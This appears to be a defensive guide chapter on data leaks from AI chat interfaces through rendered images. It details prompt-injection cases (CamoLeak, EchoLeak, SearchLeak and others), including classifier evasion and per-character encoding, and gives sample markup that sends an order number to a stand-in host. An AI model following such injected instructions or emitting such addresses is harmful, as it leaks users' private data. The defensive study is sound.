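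Copilot works with the permissions of the person asking, so it could read that person's private projects. Mayraz first had it put the encoded contents of a private project in a link, which leaked the data when the user clicked. He then tried to leak the data without a click. GitHub's pages restrict the browser to loading images from GitHub's own domains, so an image on Mayraz's server would not load directly. Camo is on one of those domains and fetches images from elsewhere, but only with a valid signature.

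GitHub will sign an outside image address for anyone who submits Markdown containing it, including through its public API. Mayraz used this to get a signed address for every letter and symbol he might need. Each address led to his own server, which returned a transparent pixel. He included the list in his hidden instructions and had Copilot write out the private text as a series of images, one for each character. The victim saw no pictures, and Mayraz could read the text from the order of the requests.

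In the shopping example, an attacker would need only ten images, one for each digit. The order number would appear in the log as five requests:

```
GET /4.png
GET /8.png
GET /2.png
GET /1.png
GET /3.png
```

The order number leaks through the model's choice of images, even though none of these addresses contains private data and the attacker knew all of them in advance. How much an attacker can learn this way depends on how many addresses the model can choose from and how many images it can load.

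Cached images would have garbled the text by dropping repeated letters. If the private text contained the word "error", a cache could have supplied the second and third "r", and the server would have received requests only for "e", "r" and "o". Mayraz avoided this by having Copilot add a new random number to the end of each signed address. Camo still accepted the addresses, presumably because its signature covers only the original image address.

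Mayraz used this method to extract the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project. He also had Copilot search a user's code for "AWS_KEY", a name programmers give to keys for Amazon's cloud services, and send him the result. Legit Security gave the Copilot flaw a severity score of 9.6 out of 10.

GitHub's 2017 reasoning was sound for the attack it addressed. HTML can capture the text that follows it, but without running a script it can't read a secret and pick a matching image for each character. A language model can do this with only instructions in ordinary language. The 2024 block on Markdown images from untrusted domains, which Willison reported for the code-editor version of Copilot Chat, wouldn't have helped either, because GitHub trusts Camo's domain.

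GitHub had fixed the flaw by 14 August 2025. According to Legit Security, it stopped displaying images in Copilot Chat entirely. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* describes the fix more generally, reporting that GitHub told Mayraz it had disallowed the use of Camo to leak sensitive user information. The flaw became public on 8 October, the date of the OECD's incident entry, *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025).

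A programming assistant loses little when images are turned off, since most of its answers are text and code. Turning them off closes the route through Camo regardless of the hidden instructions, but it doesn't by itself stop a model from putting data in a link for the user to click.

### What a proxy would need to be safe

Pictures are harder to remove from an assistant that helps people choose shoes or identify plants. A proxy could make those pictures safer to load, but it would need stricter rules than Camo had.

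The signature should be valid only in the chat the company made it for. Camo's signature depends on the image address and a shared key, and its format contains no expiry date, user or page. An address that GitHub signed for a README therefore also worked in a stranger's conversation with Copilot. A chat interface could use a separate key and include the conversation and an expiry time in the signature. Mayraz's list of addresses would then have failed, because he had obtained the signatures from another part of GitHub.

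An attacker could get around that rule if the interface signs images from the web pages its assistant reads, which it might do to show product photos. The attacker's page could contain one image for each letter of the alphabet. The interface would then sign all of those images for the user's conversation, and the model could use them to spell out private text as before.

The safest design follows Apple's approach of downloading images whether or not anyone looks at them. When the interface retrieves a web page, the proxy would fetch every image on it and store copies before the model writes its answer. If the model then uses an image, the browser loads the stored copy, and the original host receives no further request. The host's operator can tell that someone's assistant retrieved the page, but not which images the model chose or in what order.

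For this to work, the proxy has to ignore a host's request not to keep copies. It also has to reject a signed address if anything has been added to it, such as Mayraz's random numbers. Downloading every image on a page wastes bandwidth, because the assistant will use few of them. An image proxy also can't prevent leaks if the model chooses which pages to retrieve after it has read private files, since its choice of pages can carry information just as its choice of images did.

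Limiting the number of images in an answer takes less work and would have made CamoLeak much slower, since it needed a separate image for every character. According to GitHub's description of Camo, signing also makes it possible to ban addresses or limit the rate of requests. But limits protect long documents better than short secrets. Leaking a six-digit login code takes only six images, and a page of search results for shoes could easily have more.

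If the proxy can't fetch an image, the interface should leave the image out rather than let the browser request it directly. A button like Apple's Load Content would let users undo the proxy's protection with a single click.

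## Browser policies on where images may come from

CamoLeak had to go through GitHub's own proxy because GitHub's pages load images only from GitHub's domains. The browser enforces this rule. A website can send a list of allowed image servers with each page, and the browser then refuses to request images from any other server, whatever address the model writes.

The list is part of a Content Security Policy (CSP). The current draft of the standard, W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), deals mainly with attackers who get their own scripts into someone else's page. It recommends CSP as a second layer of defence behind careful handling of untrusted input. Several companies have relied on CSP much more heavily than that for image requests in a chat.

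### How the browser applies a policy

The server sends the policy in an HTTP header, a line of information sent before the page itself. The policy is a series of directives separated by semicolons, each naming a kind of content and the sources it may come from. The `img-src` directive covers images, and `default-src` covers any kind of content that has no directive of its own in the policy, which can include fonts, video, embedded frames and connections opened by scripts.

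For images, an `img-src` list replaces the `default-src` list. If a policy contains `default-src 'self'` and `img-src https://media.example`, the page can't load images from its own origin unless `img-src` also includes `'self'`. If a server sends two policies, a request has to satisfy both, so the second can't loosen the first.

The entries in these lists are called source expressions:

| Source expression | What it allows |
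|---|---|
| `'none'` | Nothing |
| `'self'` | The site that the page came from |
| `https:` | Any server, over a secure connection |
| `media.example` | Every address on that host |
| `*.media.example` | Every subdomain of that host, but not the host itself |
| `https://media.example/products/` | Addresses in that folder |
| `https://media.example/logo.png` | That one file |

No source expression can restrict the query. A policy that allows a single file also allows the same file with `?order=48213` on the end.

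The browser compares an image's address with the list of allowed sources before requesting the image. If nothing matches, it doesn't send the request. If the server replies with a redirect, the browser checks the new address before following it, but ignores the path (folders and file name) and compares only the rest, chiefly the host. Otherwise a malicious page could allow one path on another site, load an image that redirects there, and learn from the result where that site had sent the visitor. W3C calls this exception a necessary compromise.

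### Four images under a strict policy

Suppose the shopping assistant runs at chat.example and the company keeps its product photos at media.example. As before, images.example belongs to a stranger. A strict policy for the chat page might look like this:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self'; style-src 'self'; font-src 'self'; connect-src 'self';
  img-src 'self' https://media.example/products/;
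  form-action 'self'; base-uri 'none'
```

The policy starts by blocking everything and then allows what the page needs, as W3C recommends. It must set `form-action` and `base-uri` separately because `default-src` doesn't cover them. `form-action` limits where forms can send data, and `base-uri` stops injected HTML from changing the server that the page's relative URLs point to.

Now the model writes four images, three of them with the customer's order number in the address:

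| Image address | What the browser does | Who receives the order number |
|---|---|---|
| `https://chat.example/icons/parcel.png` | Loads it, because `'self'` matches | Nobody, as the address doesn't contain it |
| `https://media.example/products/boot.jpg?order=48213` | Loads it, because the host and folder match | The company, in the log of media.example |
| `https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213` | Sends nothing | Nobody |
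| `https://media.example/products/out?order=48213`, which redirects to images.example | Sends the first request and refuses to follow the redirect | The company, but not the stranger |

If the redirect in the last row led to another folder on media.example, the browser would follow it, even though the policy lists only the products folder. If media.example fetched the stranger's address itself and returned the result, the browser would make only one request, to an allowed host, and would not block it.

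Microsoft's fix for Bing Chat shows the policy working on the simplest kind of attack. When Rehberger repeated his tests after the June 2023 fix, an image on his server no longer loaded, though Bing Chat could still show pictures it had generated for the user. Embrace The Red lists the four hosts that the new policy allowed for images: th.bing.com, www.bing.com, edgeservices.bing.com and r.bing.com. Rehberger was judging from the outside and thought that Microsoft might have made other changes as well.

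### "Only trusted hosts are allowed, so nothing leaks"

A company with a policy like this might reason as follows:

1. The browser loads images only from the hosts on the list.
2. The company, or a partner it trusts, runs every host on the list.
3. Private data in an image address can therefore reach only the company or its partners.

Restricting images to a list of allowed hosts prevents leaks only if every request the model can cause falls under the policy, no host on the list forwards what it receives or stores it where outsiders can read it, and every program that displays the model's answers enforces the policy. For each condition, researchers have found products that did not meet it, and the best-documented leaks went through the allowed hosts.

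### Google's domains in Bard

In September 2023 Google's chatbot Bard, now Gemini, had just gained access to users' email and documents. Rehberger put instructions into a Google Doc, which a stranger can share with someone without asking first. When Bard read the document, it wrote an image address containing the first 20 words of the conversation. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* reports that Google's policy blocked the image when the address pointed to an outside server.

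The policy allowed every subdomain of google.com and googleusercontent.com, which included Google Apps Script. Anyone with a Google account can use this service to write a small program that runs on Google's servers when somebody opens its address. Rehberger wrote one that copied any data in the address into his own document, and found a setting that let it run for visitors who weren't logged in. The browser requested an "image" from Google, as the policy permitted, and the user's words appeared in Rehberger's document.

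Google confirmed a fix on 19 October, a month after Rehberger's report. Bard still displayed images and its policy still allowed the same broad list of sources, so he suspected that Google had begun to filter data out of image addresses.

Google made a similar exception for links in Colab, its tool for writing and running code in the browser. Colab showed a confirmation page before opening outside links the model had written, but Embrace The Red found that links to Google's own domains, including Apps Script programs, opened without one.

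### Google Forms in Superhuman and Codex

Superhuman is an email program with an AI assistant. Its policy allowed images from docs.google.com, where Google also hosts Google Forms. A form's creator can make a link with the answers already filled in, and one version of that link submits them as soon as a browser requests it.

*Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, published by the security company PromptArmor in January 2026, describes how its researchers used an image request to send email text to a form they controlled. They sent an email with hidden instructions to a test mailbox. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant included an image in its reply whose address was a link to the form, with the text of other emails filled in as the answer. The browser submitted the form when it requested the image. The user didn't need to open the malicious email.

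This route leaked far more than CamoLeak's one character per image. A single answer exposed the full text of several emails, including financial, legal and medical information, and another test extracted parts of more than 40 emails.

Superhuman could have blocked the form's address by allowing only a folder of docs.google.com that didn't contain Forms. But browsers ignore the folder after a redirect, so an attacker could still have reached the form through a redirect from another allowed address.

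The mistake in these cases was to let a page that displays a model's output load images from a host where strangers can collect data. Apps Script and Google Forms both worked as Google intended, and an ordinary security test of either service would have found nothing to repair.

In April 2026, PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* reported a very similar leak in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, which had recently gained plugins for everyday tasks. In the report, a user asked Codex for help reviewing emails, one of which contained hidden instructions, and Codex wrote an image whose address submitted the other emails to a Google Form.

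The data left by the same route as in Superhuman, but the cause may not have been the same. PromptArmor doesn't mention a browser policy in Codex, so Codex may have allowed only certain sites, including docs.google.com, or may have loaded images from anywhere. The use of a form hints at a restriction, since an attacker who can use any server doesn't need a form. But PromptArmor may also have reused a method that had worked a few months earlier. OpenAI fixed the flaw, but PromptArmor doesn't describe how.

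### EchoLeak

The most elaborate of these attacks got past four separate protections in Microsoft 365 Copilot. The security company Aim found it in January 2025 and named it EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) is Aim's own account.

The attack began with an email, which Copilot would add to the model's context only if it seemed relevant to the user's question. The researchers therefore wrote a long email with sections on common office subjects, such as starting a new job or taking leave, and repeated their instructions under each heading. Copilot then retrieved the email for many questions.

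Microsoft had a classifier meant to catch injected instructions before they reached the model. The researchers phrased their instructions as a request to the person reading the email and never mentioned AI or Copilot, and the classifier let the message through. The instructions had the model put the most sensitive information in its context into a web address. They also had it omit the email from its cited sources, so the user had no sign of where the behaviour came from.

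Copilot also removed links to outside sites from its answers, but only those in the usual Markdown form, where the address comes directly after the link's text. It missed links in Markdown's other form, which puts the address on a separate line and refers to it by a label. Such a link could leak data if the user clicked it. Copilot also missed images written this way, which the browser would request without a click.

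The browser policy then stopped the attack, because the researchers' server wasn't on Microsoft's list. They searched the list for a host that would pass the data on. It had 29 different entries, 11 of which covered all the subdomains of a domain. The list included hosts for icons, LinkedIn pictures, Bing, SharePoint and Teams.

One entry in the policy allowed every subdomain of sharepoint.com. Each organisation that uses SharePoint gets its own subdomain, so the policy also allowed an attacker's own site. SharePoint has a service that fetches content from another address to embed it in a page, and the researchers could use it to forward the data. The attack worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, which few people would do.

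Teams had a similar service that lacked that condition and fetched any web address included in the request. The researchers had Copilot write an image address on the Teams domain that contained their own server's address and the stolen data. The browser's policy allowed that Microsoft host, so the browser sent the request. Teams then requested the researchers' address, and the data arrived in their log.

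| Protection in Copilot | How the attack got past it |
|---|---|
| Classifier for injected instructions | The instructions read like a request to a person |
| Removal of outside links and images | The address was on a separate line, in a form the code didn't recognise |
| Browser policy on image sources | An allowed Teams service fetched the outside address |
| Citation of sources | The instructions told the model not to mention the email |

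The browser followed the policy throughout. The request that reached the stranger came from a company's server, and browser policies don't apply to server-side requests. Ravia states that no setting available to a customer's administrators would have prevented the leak. Microsoft finished repairing the flaw on its own servers in May 2025 and published an advisory on 11 June. It had no evidence that anyone had used it against customers.

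Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application. Samoilenko's and Rehberger's 2023 image attacks also needed no click to send the data, but the user had to paste the attacker's text or open the attacker's page. In EchoLeak, the user only had to ask Copilot a question about a common subject.

The academic case study *EchoLeak* recommends a policy that allows only the company's own hosts that the application needs, with no wildcards. It predicts that this would block the attack, but it analyzes published information and includes no experiments. Limiting the list to the company's own hosts would not have been enough here, because Microsoft owns Teams. The rule about need is more useful because it would have led somebody to ask why Copilot's page had to load images from that particular Teams service and whether another host could supply them.

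### Products and pages without the policy

A policy protects only the pages served with it, and companies often display a model's answers in several places. On 24 July 2023, weeks after the Bing Chat repair, Rehberger reported the same kind of leak in Azure AI Playground, a Microsoft page where developers try out models. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* rates it less serious because the page couldn't yet retrieve outside content, so a user would have had to paste in an attacker's text. As far as Rehberger could tell, Microsoft fixed the leak by inserting a space into the Markdown so the page no longer treated it as an image.

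The company behind Superhuman had a similar gap. Its email program at least restricted image sources, but Superhuman Go, a newer assistant that reads web pages and connects to services such as Gmail and Stripe, loaded an image from a domain belonging to researchers at PromptArmor. In their test, the user was viewing a review site that contained hidden instructions and asked whether any emails would help in answering the bad reviews. The assistant put financial figures from an email into the address of a one-pixel image. Grammarly, another of the company's products, had the same fault, but less data was at risk because its assistant seemed to read only the user's own document and questions.

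The company turned off the vulnerable features on the first working day after the report and fixed the email program a day later. It patched its other products nine days after that.

The same problem can arise within a single product if, for example, the page for shared conversations lacks the policy. A company can avoid this by having its servers add the header to every page by default, so that a developer would have to remove it deliberately.

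Browser extensions are another exception. W3C advises browsers not to let a site's policy interfere with extensions the user has installed, and Chrome ensures that content added by an extension works regardless of the page's rules. An extension that displays a model's answers inside other websites therefore needs its own protection against remote images.

A company can also send the header in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations but still loads the content. This helps the company find out what a new policy would break, but the page has no protection until the company switches to the enforcing header. The reports include the address of the blocked request, which in a chat may contain the data that the policy kept from leaving. If another company collects the reports, it receives that data.

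### Requests that an image list doesn't cover

A policy that restricts images can still let data leave through other requests. W3C gives the example of a policy that forbids all images, scripts and fonts but has no `default-src` directive. That policy still allows a prefetch, which loads a page in advance in case the user opens it, because only `default-src` covers prefetches. Even with `default-src` set, the browser allows a prefetch to any server listed anywhere in the policy, so a host that the company approved only for fonts can receive one. Adding `img-src *` to a policy with a strict default is also a mistake, because it lets images load from any server.

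Whether a model can trigger a prefetch depends on the renderer. Ordinary Markdown has no syntax for a prefetch, but if the renderer also accepts raw HTML, the model may be able to add an element that triggers one.

Some kinds of connection fall outside CSP or fit it badly. Mike West, a Google engineer who works on browser security, gives two examples in a newer proposal: looking up server names in advance, and WebRTC, the technology behind video calls in the browser (West, in *Connection Allowlists*). A name lookup may sound harmless, but the name itself can contain data. Suppose an element on the chat page makes the browser look up this name:

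```
48213.images.example
```

The lookup normally ends at a name server chosen by the owner of images.example, who can read the order number from the lookup without receiving any request for a page or image. Cardwell's iPhone test found a simpler version of this leak in email, where the sender could tell from a lookup that a message had arrived. WebRTC matters mainly for pages that run code written by a model, because using it requires a script.

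CSP can restrict where a form sends data, but the current draft has no directive that restricts which pages a user can visit by clicking a link. A strict policy can therefore block an image that leaks data without a click, but if the model writes a link instead, the data can still leak when the user clicks it. The chat interface needs another control for links.

A page's policy on image sources does not apply when the assistant itself visits a website. Superhuman's assistant could open any web address to look something up. PromptArmor got it to open an address with email text in the query string, which sent the text to that site without an image or a Google Form.

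### Choosing the list

Bing Chat's policy had four entries and Copilot's had 29. A shorter list leaves an attacker fewer services to search through, but the number of entries matters less than what runs on each host. Superhuman's leak needed only one entry, and one of Bing Chat's four, www.bing.com, serves a whole search engine. In SearchLeak, three years later, data leaked through a Bing service that Copilot's policy allowed.

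The safest host to allow is one that only serves pictures the company has put there. It ignores the query, which is the part of an address after the question mark, and never redirects or fetches from another server. If the model adds an order number to an address on this host, the number reaches only the company's log. The company already has the conversation, so it learns nothing new, but it should protect the log as carefully as the conversation or not record the query at all.

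A proxy can download and store images from other websites before the model writes its answer. The browser policy then needs only one entry for images, and it prevents a mistake elsewhere in the interface from sending the browser to a stranger's server. If the renderer misses an unusual way of writing an image and leaves the original address in place, as Copilot's link filter did, the proxy can't help, but the browser policy will block that address.

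This takes more work than adding hosts to a list. Copilot's policy included separate hosts for connector icons, SharePoint files and designer images, and a dedicated host would mean copying all of those or serving them through a common address. Product teams will tend to ask for another entry because it takes a minute. A company that agrees to one should check whether anything on the host:

- lets outsiders publish pages or run programs;
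- fetches or redirects to an address that it receives in a request;
- stores submitted data where an outsider can read it;
- shows outsiders how often, or when, somebody loaded a file.

The last point follows from CamoLeak, where the attacker worked out the text by seeing which images the browser requested. A file-sharing service that shows its users a download count for each file could leak text in the same way, even if it keeps no other information about the requests.

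The company also has to repeat the check when a host changes. Wildcards make this nearly impossible because they cover future services, whose teams may never have heard of the chat product. Listing hosts by their full names at least blocks new services by default.

### Connection Allowlists

Browsers now have the beginnings of a broader control. West argues that CSP sorts requests into too many types for a site that simply wants to stop data from leaving, since a leak through a font request does as much damage as one through an image. The proposal, Connection Allowlists, replaces the separate lists with a single one for every connection the page makes. For the shopping assistant, the header could be:

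```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://media.example/*")
```

The first entry stands for the site that sent the page. According to Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026), the browser checks each destination before connecting, and the list covers images, scripts, redirects, WebRTC, advance DNS lookups and navigation to other pages. The announcement names AI-generated code as one of the main uses.

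West's draft treats redirects more strictly than CSP does. It blocks every redirected request, even if the new address is on the list, though this is still an open question in the draft. Helme writes in *Connection Allowlist* that redirects and WebRTC are both blocked by default, but a site can choose to allow them. In the earlier example, both controls would block the image that redirected from media.example to the stranger's server. A redirect from one folder of media.example to another would pass under CSP but fail under West's draft.

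Chrome tested the feature on live websites, then released it to ordinary users in version 152 on 25 August 2026 (Chrome for Developers' *Chrome 152* (2026)). Microsoft ran its own trial for Edge. In March, *Intent to Experiment* (Chromestatus, 2026), a notice to Chromium developers, recorded no position from Firefox or WebKit, the engine behind Safari. Shortly before Chrome's release, CentralCSP's *Connection Allowlists, a network egress sandbox in the browser* still reported no sign of support from Firefox or Safari and advised websites not to depend on the feature.

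A short list can cause trouble on a page used for ordinary browsing. Two days after the release, Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026) warned that users might be unable to sign in through another company's account if the site left that company off its list. The problem is larger for a chat page, because its answers link to sources all over the web. The list also covers navigation to other pages, so a strict one may block those links. Blocking them would also stop one-click leaks, but few companies would accept an assistant whose citations don't open. The control is easier to use on a separate frame that runs generated code and doesn't need links.

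West also describes ways around the list. The list applies only to one page, so a script could look for another page on the same site with looser rules, or pass data to another window that isn't subject to the list. Both methods require a script, so an image in a Markdown answer can't use them.

Connection Allowlists would not have prevented the Bard leak, EchoLeak, or the leak through Superhuman's form if the companies had put the same hosts on the list. In each case the browser connected only to a server that the company had approved. The feature helps with requests that CSP doesn't cover, but the company still has to check what each approved server does with the URL it receives.

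## Checking model output before it is displayed

A browser policy blocks a request after the interface has put the image on the page. The company can act earlier with a sanitiser, which is code that removes or disarms dangerous elements before the interface displays the output. A sanitiser can enforce rules that a browser policy can't express, such as rejecting every image address that has a query. But it has to recognise an image in any form the model might write, and finish before the browser starts loading the image.

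### Four forms of one answer

An answer goes through four forms on its way to the screen, and a company can put a filter at any of them.

| Form | What happens | What a filter can examine |
|---|---|---|
| Streamed text | The model writes the answer in small pieces, and the server passes them on as they arrive | Characters |
| Parsed Markdown | A parser works out which characters are formatting and builds a tree of paragraphs, links and images | Each image and link, with its address |
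| HTML | The renderer writes the tree out as HTML | Elements and their attributes |
| Live page | The browser turns the HTML into page elements and requests the images | The finished page, after the requests have started |

Some renderers skip the third form and create page elements directly from the tree.

A filter on the streamed text usually searches for a pattern, such as an exclamation mark followed by square brackets and then an address in round ones. The shopping assistant could write its parcel image in at least three ways, and that pattern finds only the first:

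```
![Parcel](https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213)

![Parcel][p]

[p]: https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213

<img src="https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213">
```

The second form is the labelled one that Copilot's filter missed in EchoLeak. The third is HTML, which CommonMark lets writers mix with Markdown. A developer can add patterns for both, but they would also have to handle angle brackets around an address, a title after it, and numeric codes in place of ordinary characters, all of which CommonMark allows. The filter also deletes harmless text. If a user asks how to write an image in Markdown, it will remove the example from the answer.

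Filtering the tree that the Markdown parser produces avoids this problem. The parser turns both Markdown versions of the parcel image into the same kind of node, with the full address attached, and turns an example inside a code block into a code node, so the filter needs only one rule for images. That rule doesn't cover raw HTML, which a Markdown parser passes through without interpreting. The simplest solution is to display raw HTML as plain text, since Markdown covers nearly everything a chat model needs to express.

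An interface that needs HTML has to filter that as well. Many HTML elements can trigger a request, as EFAIL showed in email, so the filter should permit only a short list of elements and attributes. Developers often use a general-purpose HTML sanitiser for this, but these tools are mainly meant to stop scripts and may let ordinary images through.

The filter can cause the leak itself. A browser requests an image even if its element is never added to the visible page. If a sanitiser uses the live page's document to parse the HTML into elements, the browser may send the request during the inspection. Browsers provide inert documents, in which images don't load, for this kind of inspection.

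Once the image is on the live page, a script that finds and deletes it comes too late, and hiding the image doesn't help either. In a demonstration for Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, no picture appeared in Copilot Chat, but the request still reached the researchers' server with a secret key in its address. (The security company had cancelled the key beforehand.)

### A renderer that checks first

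The following pseudocode parses the answer, checks the tree and only then changes the page:

```
PLAIN = paragraph, heading, list, emphasis, table, code, text

function show(answerSoFar, page):
    tree = parseMarkdown(answerSoFar)

    for each node in tree:
        if node is an image:
            if not mayLoad(node.address):
                replace node with placeholder("Image not loaded")
        else if node is a link:
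            if not mayLink(node.address):
                replace node with its text, not clickable
        else if node.type is not in PLAIN:
            replace node with its original characters

    page.replaceAnswer(buildElements(tree))

function mayLoad(address):
    url = parseAddress(address)
    return url is valid
       and url.scheme is "https"
       and url.host is exactly "media.example"
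       and url.path starts with "/products/"
       and url.query is empty
```

The renderer changes the page only in the last line of `show`, so an image stays off the page if the parser fails or `mayLoad` can't interpret its address. The list of plain types protects against features added later. If a developer adds video support to the parser, the renderer will display the video's Markdown as text until the developer also writes a rule for its address. If the interface turns some code blocks into diagrams, those need checking too, because a diagram can load images.

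`mayLoad` is stricter than the `img-src` list, which would accept `boot.jpg?order=48213` from the same host. The company can also check the address against its catalogue, so that only existing pictures load. The browser policy is still useful as a second barrier.

The function splits the address into its parts before comparing them because searching the whole address for a trusted name is unsafe. Suppose a filter only looked for ".media.example/" somewhere in the address. It would accept this one, whose host is images.example:

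```
https://images.example/.media.example/parcel.png
```

Microsoft's code editor, VS Code, contained this mistake. Its assistant, Copilot Chat, could fetch web pages without the user's confirmation if the site was on a list of trusted domains. According to GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections*, the check compared the address with a text pattern instead of parsing it, so an untrusted address passed if its path contained a trusted name. A GitHub researcher used this flaw to have the assistant read a login token from a local file and send it to an outside site without confirmation. The leak used the fetching tool, but the same list also decided which remote images the chat could show.

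### Why streaming makes timing matter

A long answer takes a while to write, so chat interfaces display it as it arrives. The renderer therefore runs many times on unfinished text. At one moment it may have the first of these lines, and a fraction of a second later the second:

```
![Parcel](https://images.example/parcel.png?order=482
![Parcel](https://images.example/parcel.png?order=48213)
```

While a model streams its answer, a Markdown parser treats an image link as plain text until the closing bracket arrives. The parser then turns the link into an image, and the browser can request it while the model is still writing. A check that waits for the end of the answer can therefore run after the request has sent the data.

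The filter also has to check the whole answer so far each time a new piece arrives, which is why `show` receives all of it and not just the latest piece. An address may be split between two pieces, so that neither looks suspicious alone. The model can also write an image with a label and define the label several paragraphs later, which turns text the filter has already passed into an image. Some renderers complete unfinished formatting so that the user doesn't see stray punctuation. They have to check the address after completing it, or the browser may request an unchecked, half-written address.

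Parsing the whole answer again each time a new piece arrives takes more computing. A company can reduce this computing by updating the page only a few times a second, or by showing placeholders for all images until the answer is complete and then checking them together. With placeholders, the text still appears immediately, and the reader waits a little longer for pictures. Holding images back also lets the interface limit the number of images before any of them loads.

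### SearchLeak

Taler, a researcher at the security company Varonis, published SearchLeak on 15 June 2026. The attack combined three weaknesses in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise, and the second was a check that ran too late.

The first was the search query in the victim's link, which Copilot treated as instructions. Varonis had already found the same weakness in the consumer version of Microsoft's Copilot, in an attack it called Reprompt, and was surprised to find it in the business version too, which should have had more safeguards. The instructions had Copilot put the email title into the address of an HTML image.

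Microsoft had anticipated HTML in Copilot's answers. Its code wrapped such output in a code block, so that the browser would show the HTML as text and not load anything. But the events happened in this order:

1. Copilot began to stream its answer, which included the image element.
2. The page put the unfinished answer on the screen as raw HTML, and the browser requested the image.
3. Copilot finished the answer.
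4. The code wrapped the HTML in a code block, where it appeared as harmless text.

This is a race condition, a fault where the outcome depends on which of two events happens first. Someone who tested Copilot by looking at finished answers would have seen the protection work every time.

The browser policy on Copilot's page didn't allow images from the attacker's server, but it did allow every subdomain of bing.com. Bing's search by image accepts the web address of a picture, which Bing's own server then fetches. The image address that Copilot wrote therefore pointed to Bing and contained a second address on the attacker's server, with the email title in it. The browser sent the request to Bing, Bing's server requested the second address, and the title appeared in the attacker's log. The victim may have noticed Copilot thinking and then an odd answer, but by then the attacker already had the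 title.

The attack needed all three weaknesses. If Microsoft's code had wrapped the output before the page displayed it, the browser would not have created the image element, whichever hosts the policy allowed. Taler recommends treating streamed output as untrusted and sanitising it as the page renders it. He also advises companies to check their browser policies for hosts that fetch addresses supplied by users.

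Microsoft published its notice, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), eleven days before Varonis published its account. The notice lists the flaw as CVE-2026-42824, with no known exploitation and no action required from customers. It classifies the flaw as command injection, which fits the search query better than the late wrapping or Bing's fetching. Neither Microsoft nor Taler specifies which of the three weaknesses Microsoft fixed.

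The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* reported that Microsoft rated the flaw "critical" but scored its severity at 6.5 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5. Both scores are lower than "critical" suggests. Microsoft scored it as a flaw that requires the victim to click something. The standard formula gives 7.5 for an otherwise identical flaw that needs no click.

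### Notion AI and the late approval

Notion, a program for shared documents, had a similar fault in a feature that asked for the user's approval. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a test in which a user uploaded a job applicant's résumé and asked the assistant to update a document that tracked candidates. The assistant followed hidden instructions in the résumé. It collected the document's text, added it to an address on the researchers' server and inserted an image with that address into the document.

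Notion saved the edit before warning the user about the outside site and asking whether to trust it, so the browser had already requested the image. Whatever the user answered, the researchers' log contained salary expectations, notes on candidates and diversity hiring goals.

Notion's warning failed because the program treated an unapproved edit as part of the live document, a fault that did not depend on streaming. The warning correctly identified an unknown site and showed an address containing the user's data, so an attentive user would have had enough information to refuse.

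GitHub's researcher found that VS Code's file-editing tool also wrote changes to disk before asking the user whether to "keep" or "undo" them. Another program could therefore act on the new file before the user answered. When the researcher had the assistant change a settings file, VS Code immediately started a program named in that file.

Notion's case also shows that a sanitiser in the chat window isn't enough if the assistant can write elsewhere. In the test, the image loaded from the user's document. PromptArmor found that Notion's email program also loaded Markdown images in drafts its assistant wrote, though this assistant seemed to have access only to material the user mentioned. A company has to apply the same check wherever the model's text can appear, and previews of edits awaiting approval must not load anything from outside.

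PromptArmor reported the flaw on 24 December 2025. Five days later HackerOne, which received Notion's bug reports, closed it as "Not Applicable". Notion's staff learned of it when PromptArmor published its findings on 7 January, and had a fix for the document edits running that night.

### What products do with outside images

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes a Markdown sanitiser in Gemini that identifies external image addresses and doesn't display the images. Google says this makes attacks like EchoLeak inapplicable to Gemini. Bard, Gemini's predecessor, still displayed images from any Google domain.

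Outside researchers have found signs that the newer protection works. Tenable, a security company, reports in *The Trifecta* that Gemini filtered or restricted images and links in its answers and sent links through a google.com address. Tenable therefore looked for a way to send data out through one of Gemini's tools. The sanitiser had closed the route through rendered output, but Gemini could still make requests that never passed through the renderer.

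Rehberger reported in February 2024 that Copilot Chat in VS Code loaded images from any address, and he showed that instructions in a source file could make it send out earlier parts of the conversation. GitHub confirmed the bug in March and the fix in June. Rehberger thought that Copilot Chat no longer displayed Markdown images after the fix, while Willison wrote that GitHub had disabled only those from untrusted domains. Vulners' *GitHub*, a summary of a bug report on Copilot's client programs, also describes a rule that permits images from trusted domains, and a warning about links.

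A later security notice from VS Code supports Willison's version. Through version 1.100.0, the editor used its list of trusted domains to decide whether a remote image could appear in the chat. The same list determined when the editor warned users before opening a link in the browser, and it included every subdomain of microsoft.com and github.com. After learning of the flaw, VS Code's developers concluded that a chat raises more security concerns than opening a link does. Version 1.100.1, released in May 2025, removed support for remote images in the chat.

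Continue, another programming assistant for VS Code, chose to ask the user. VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* describes two attacks on it. In one, the instructions were in a comment in a code file, and the data was sent as soon as the user asked Continue to analyze the file. In the other, the instructions were on a web page, which Continue fetched with the user's permission. It then read a local file of the kind in which programmers store passwords and put its contents into an image address, without giving the user a chance to refuse the image.

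VerSprite reported this on 20 August 2025, and Continue's developers released a fix the next day. The program now asks before it loads an external image and limits which files the assistant can read. The developers of Cline, a similar assistant, had not fixed the same flaw more than 90 days after Rehberger reported it on 29 May, according to Embrace The Red's *Cline*. Nobody seemed to be reading reports submitted through the project's security page.

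Companies that build their own chatbots from open-source software shouldn't assume that it has a filter. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, veganmosfet tested dify, a platform for building applications on language models. Its chat page loaded Markdown images from any domain and had no browser policy for images by default. veganmosfet put a sentence in a PDF that the chatbot could search, and when a user asked about the PDF's subject, the user's name went out in an image address.

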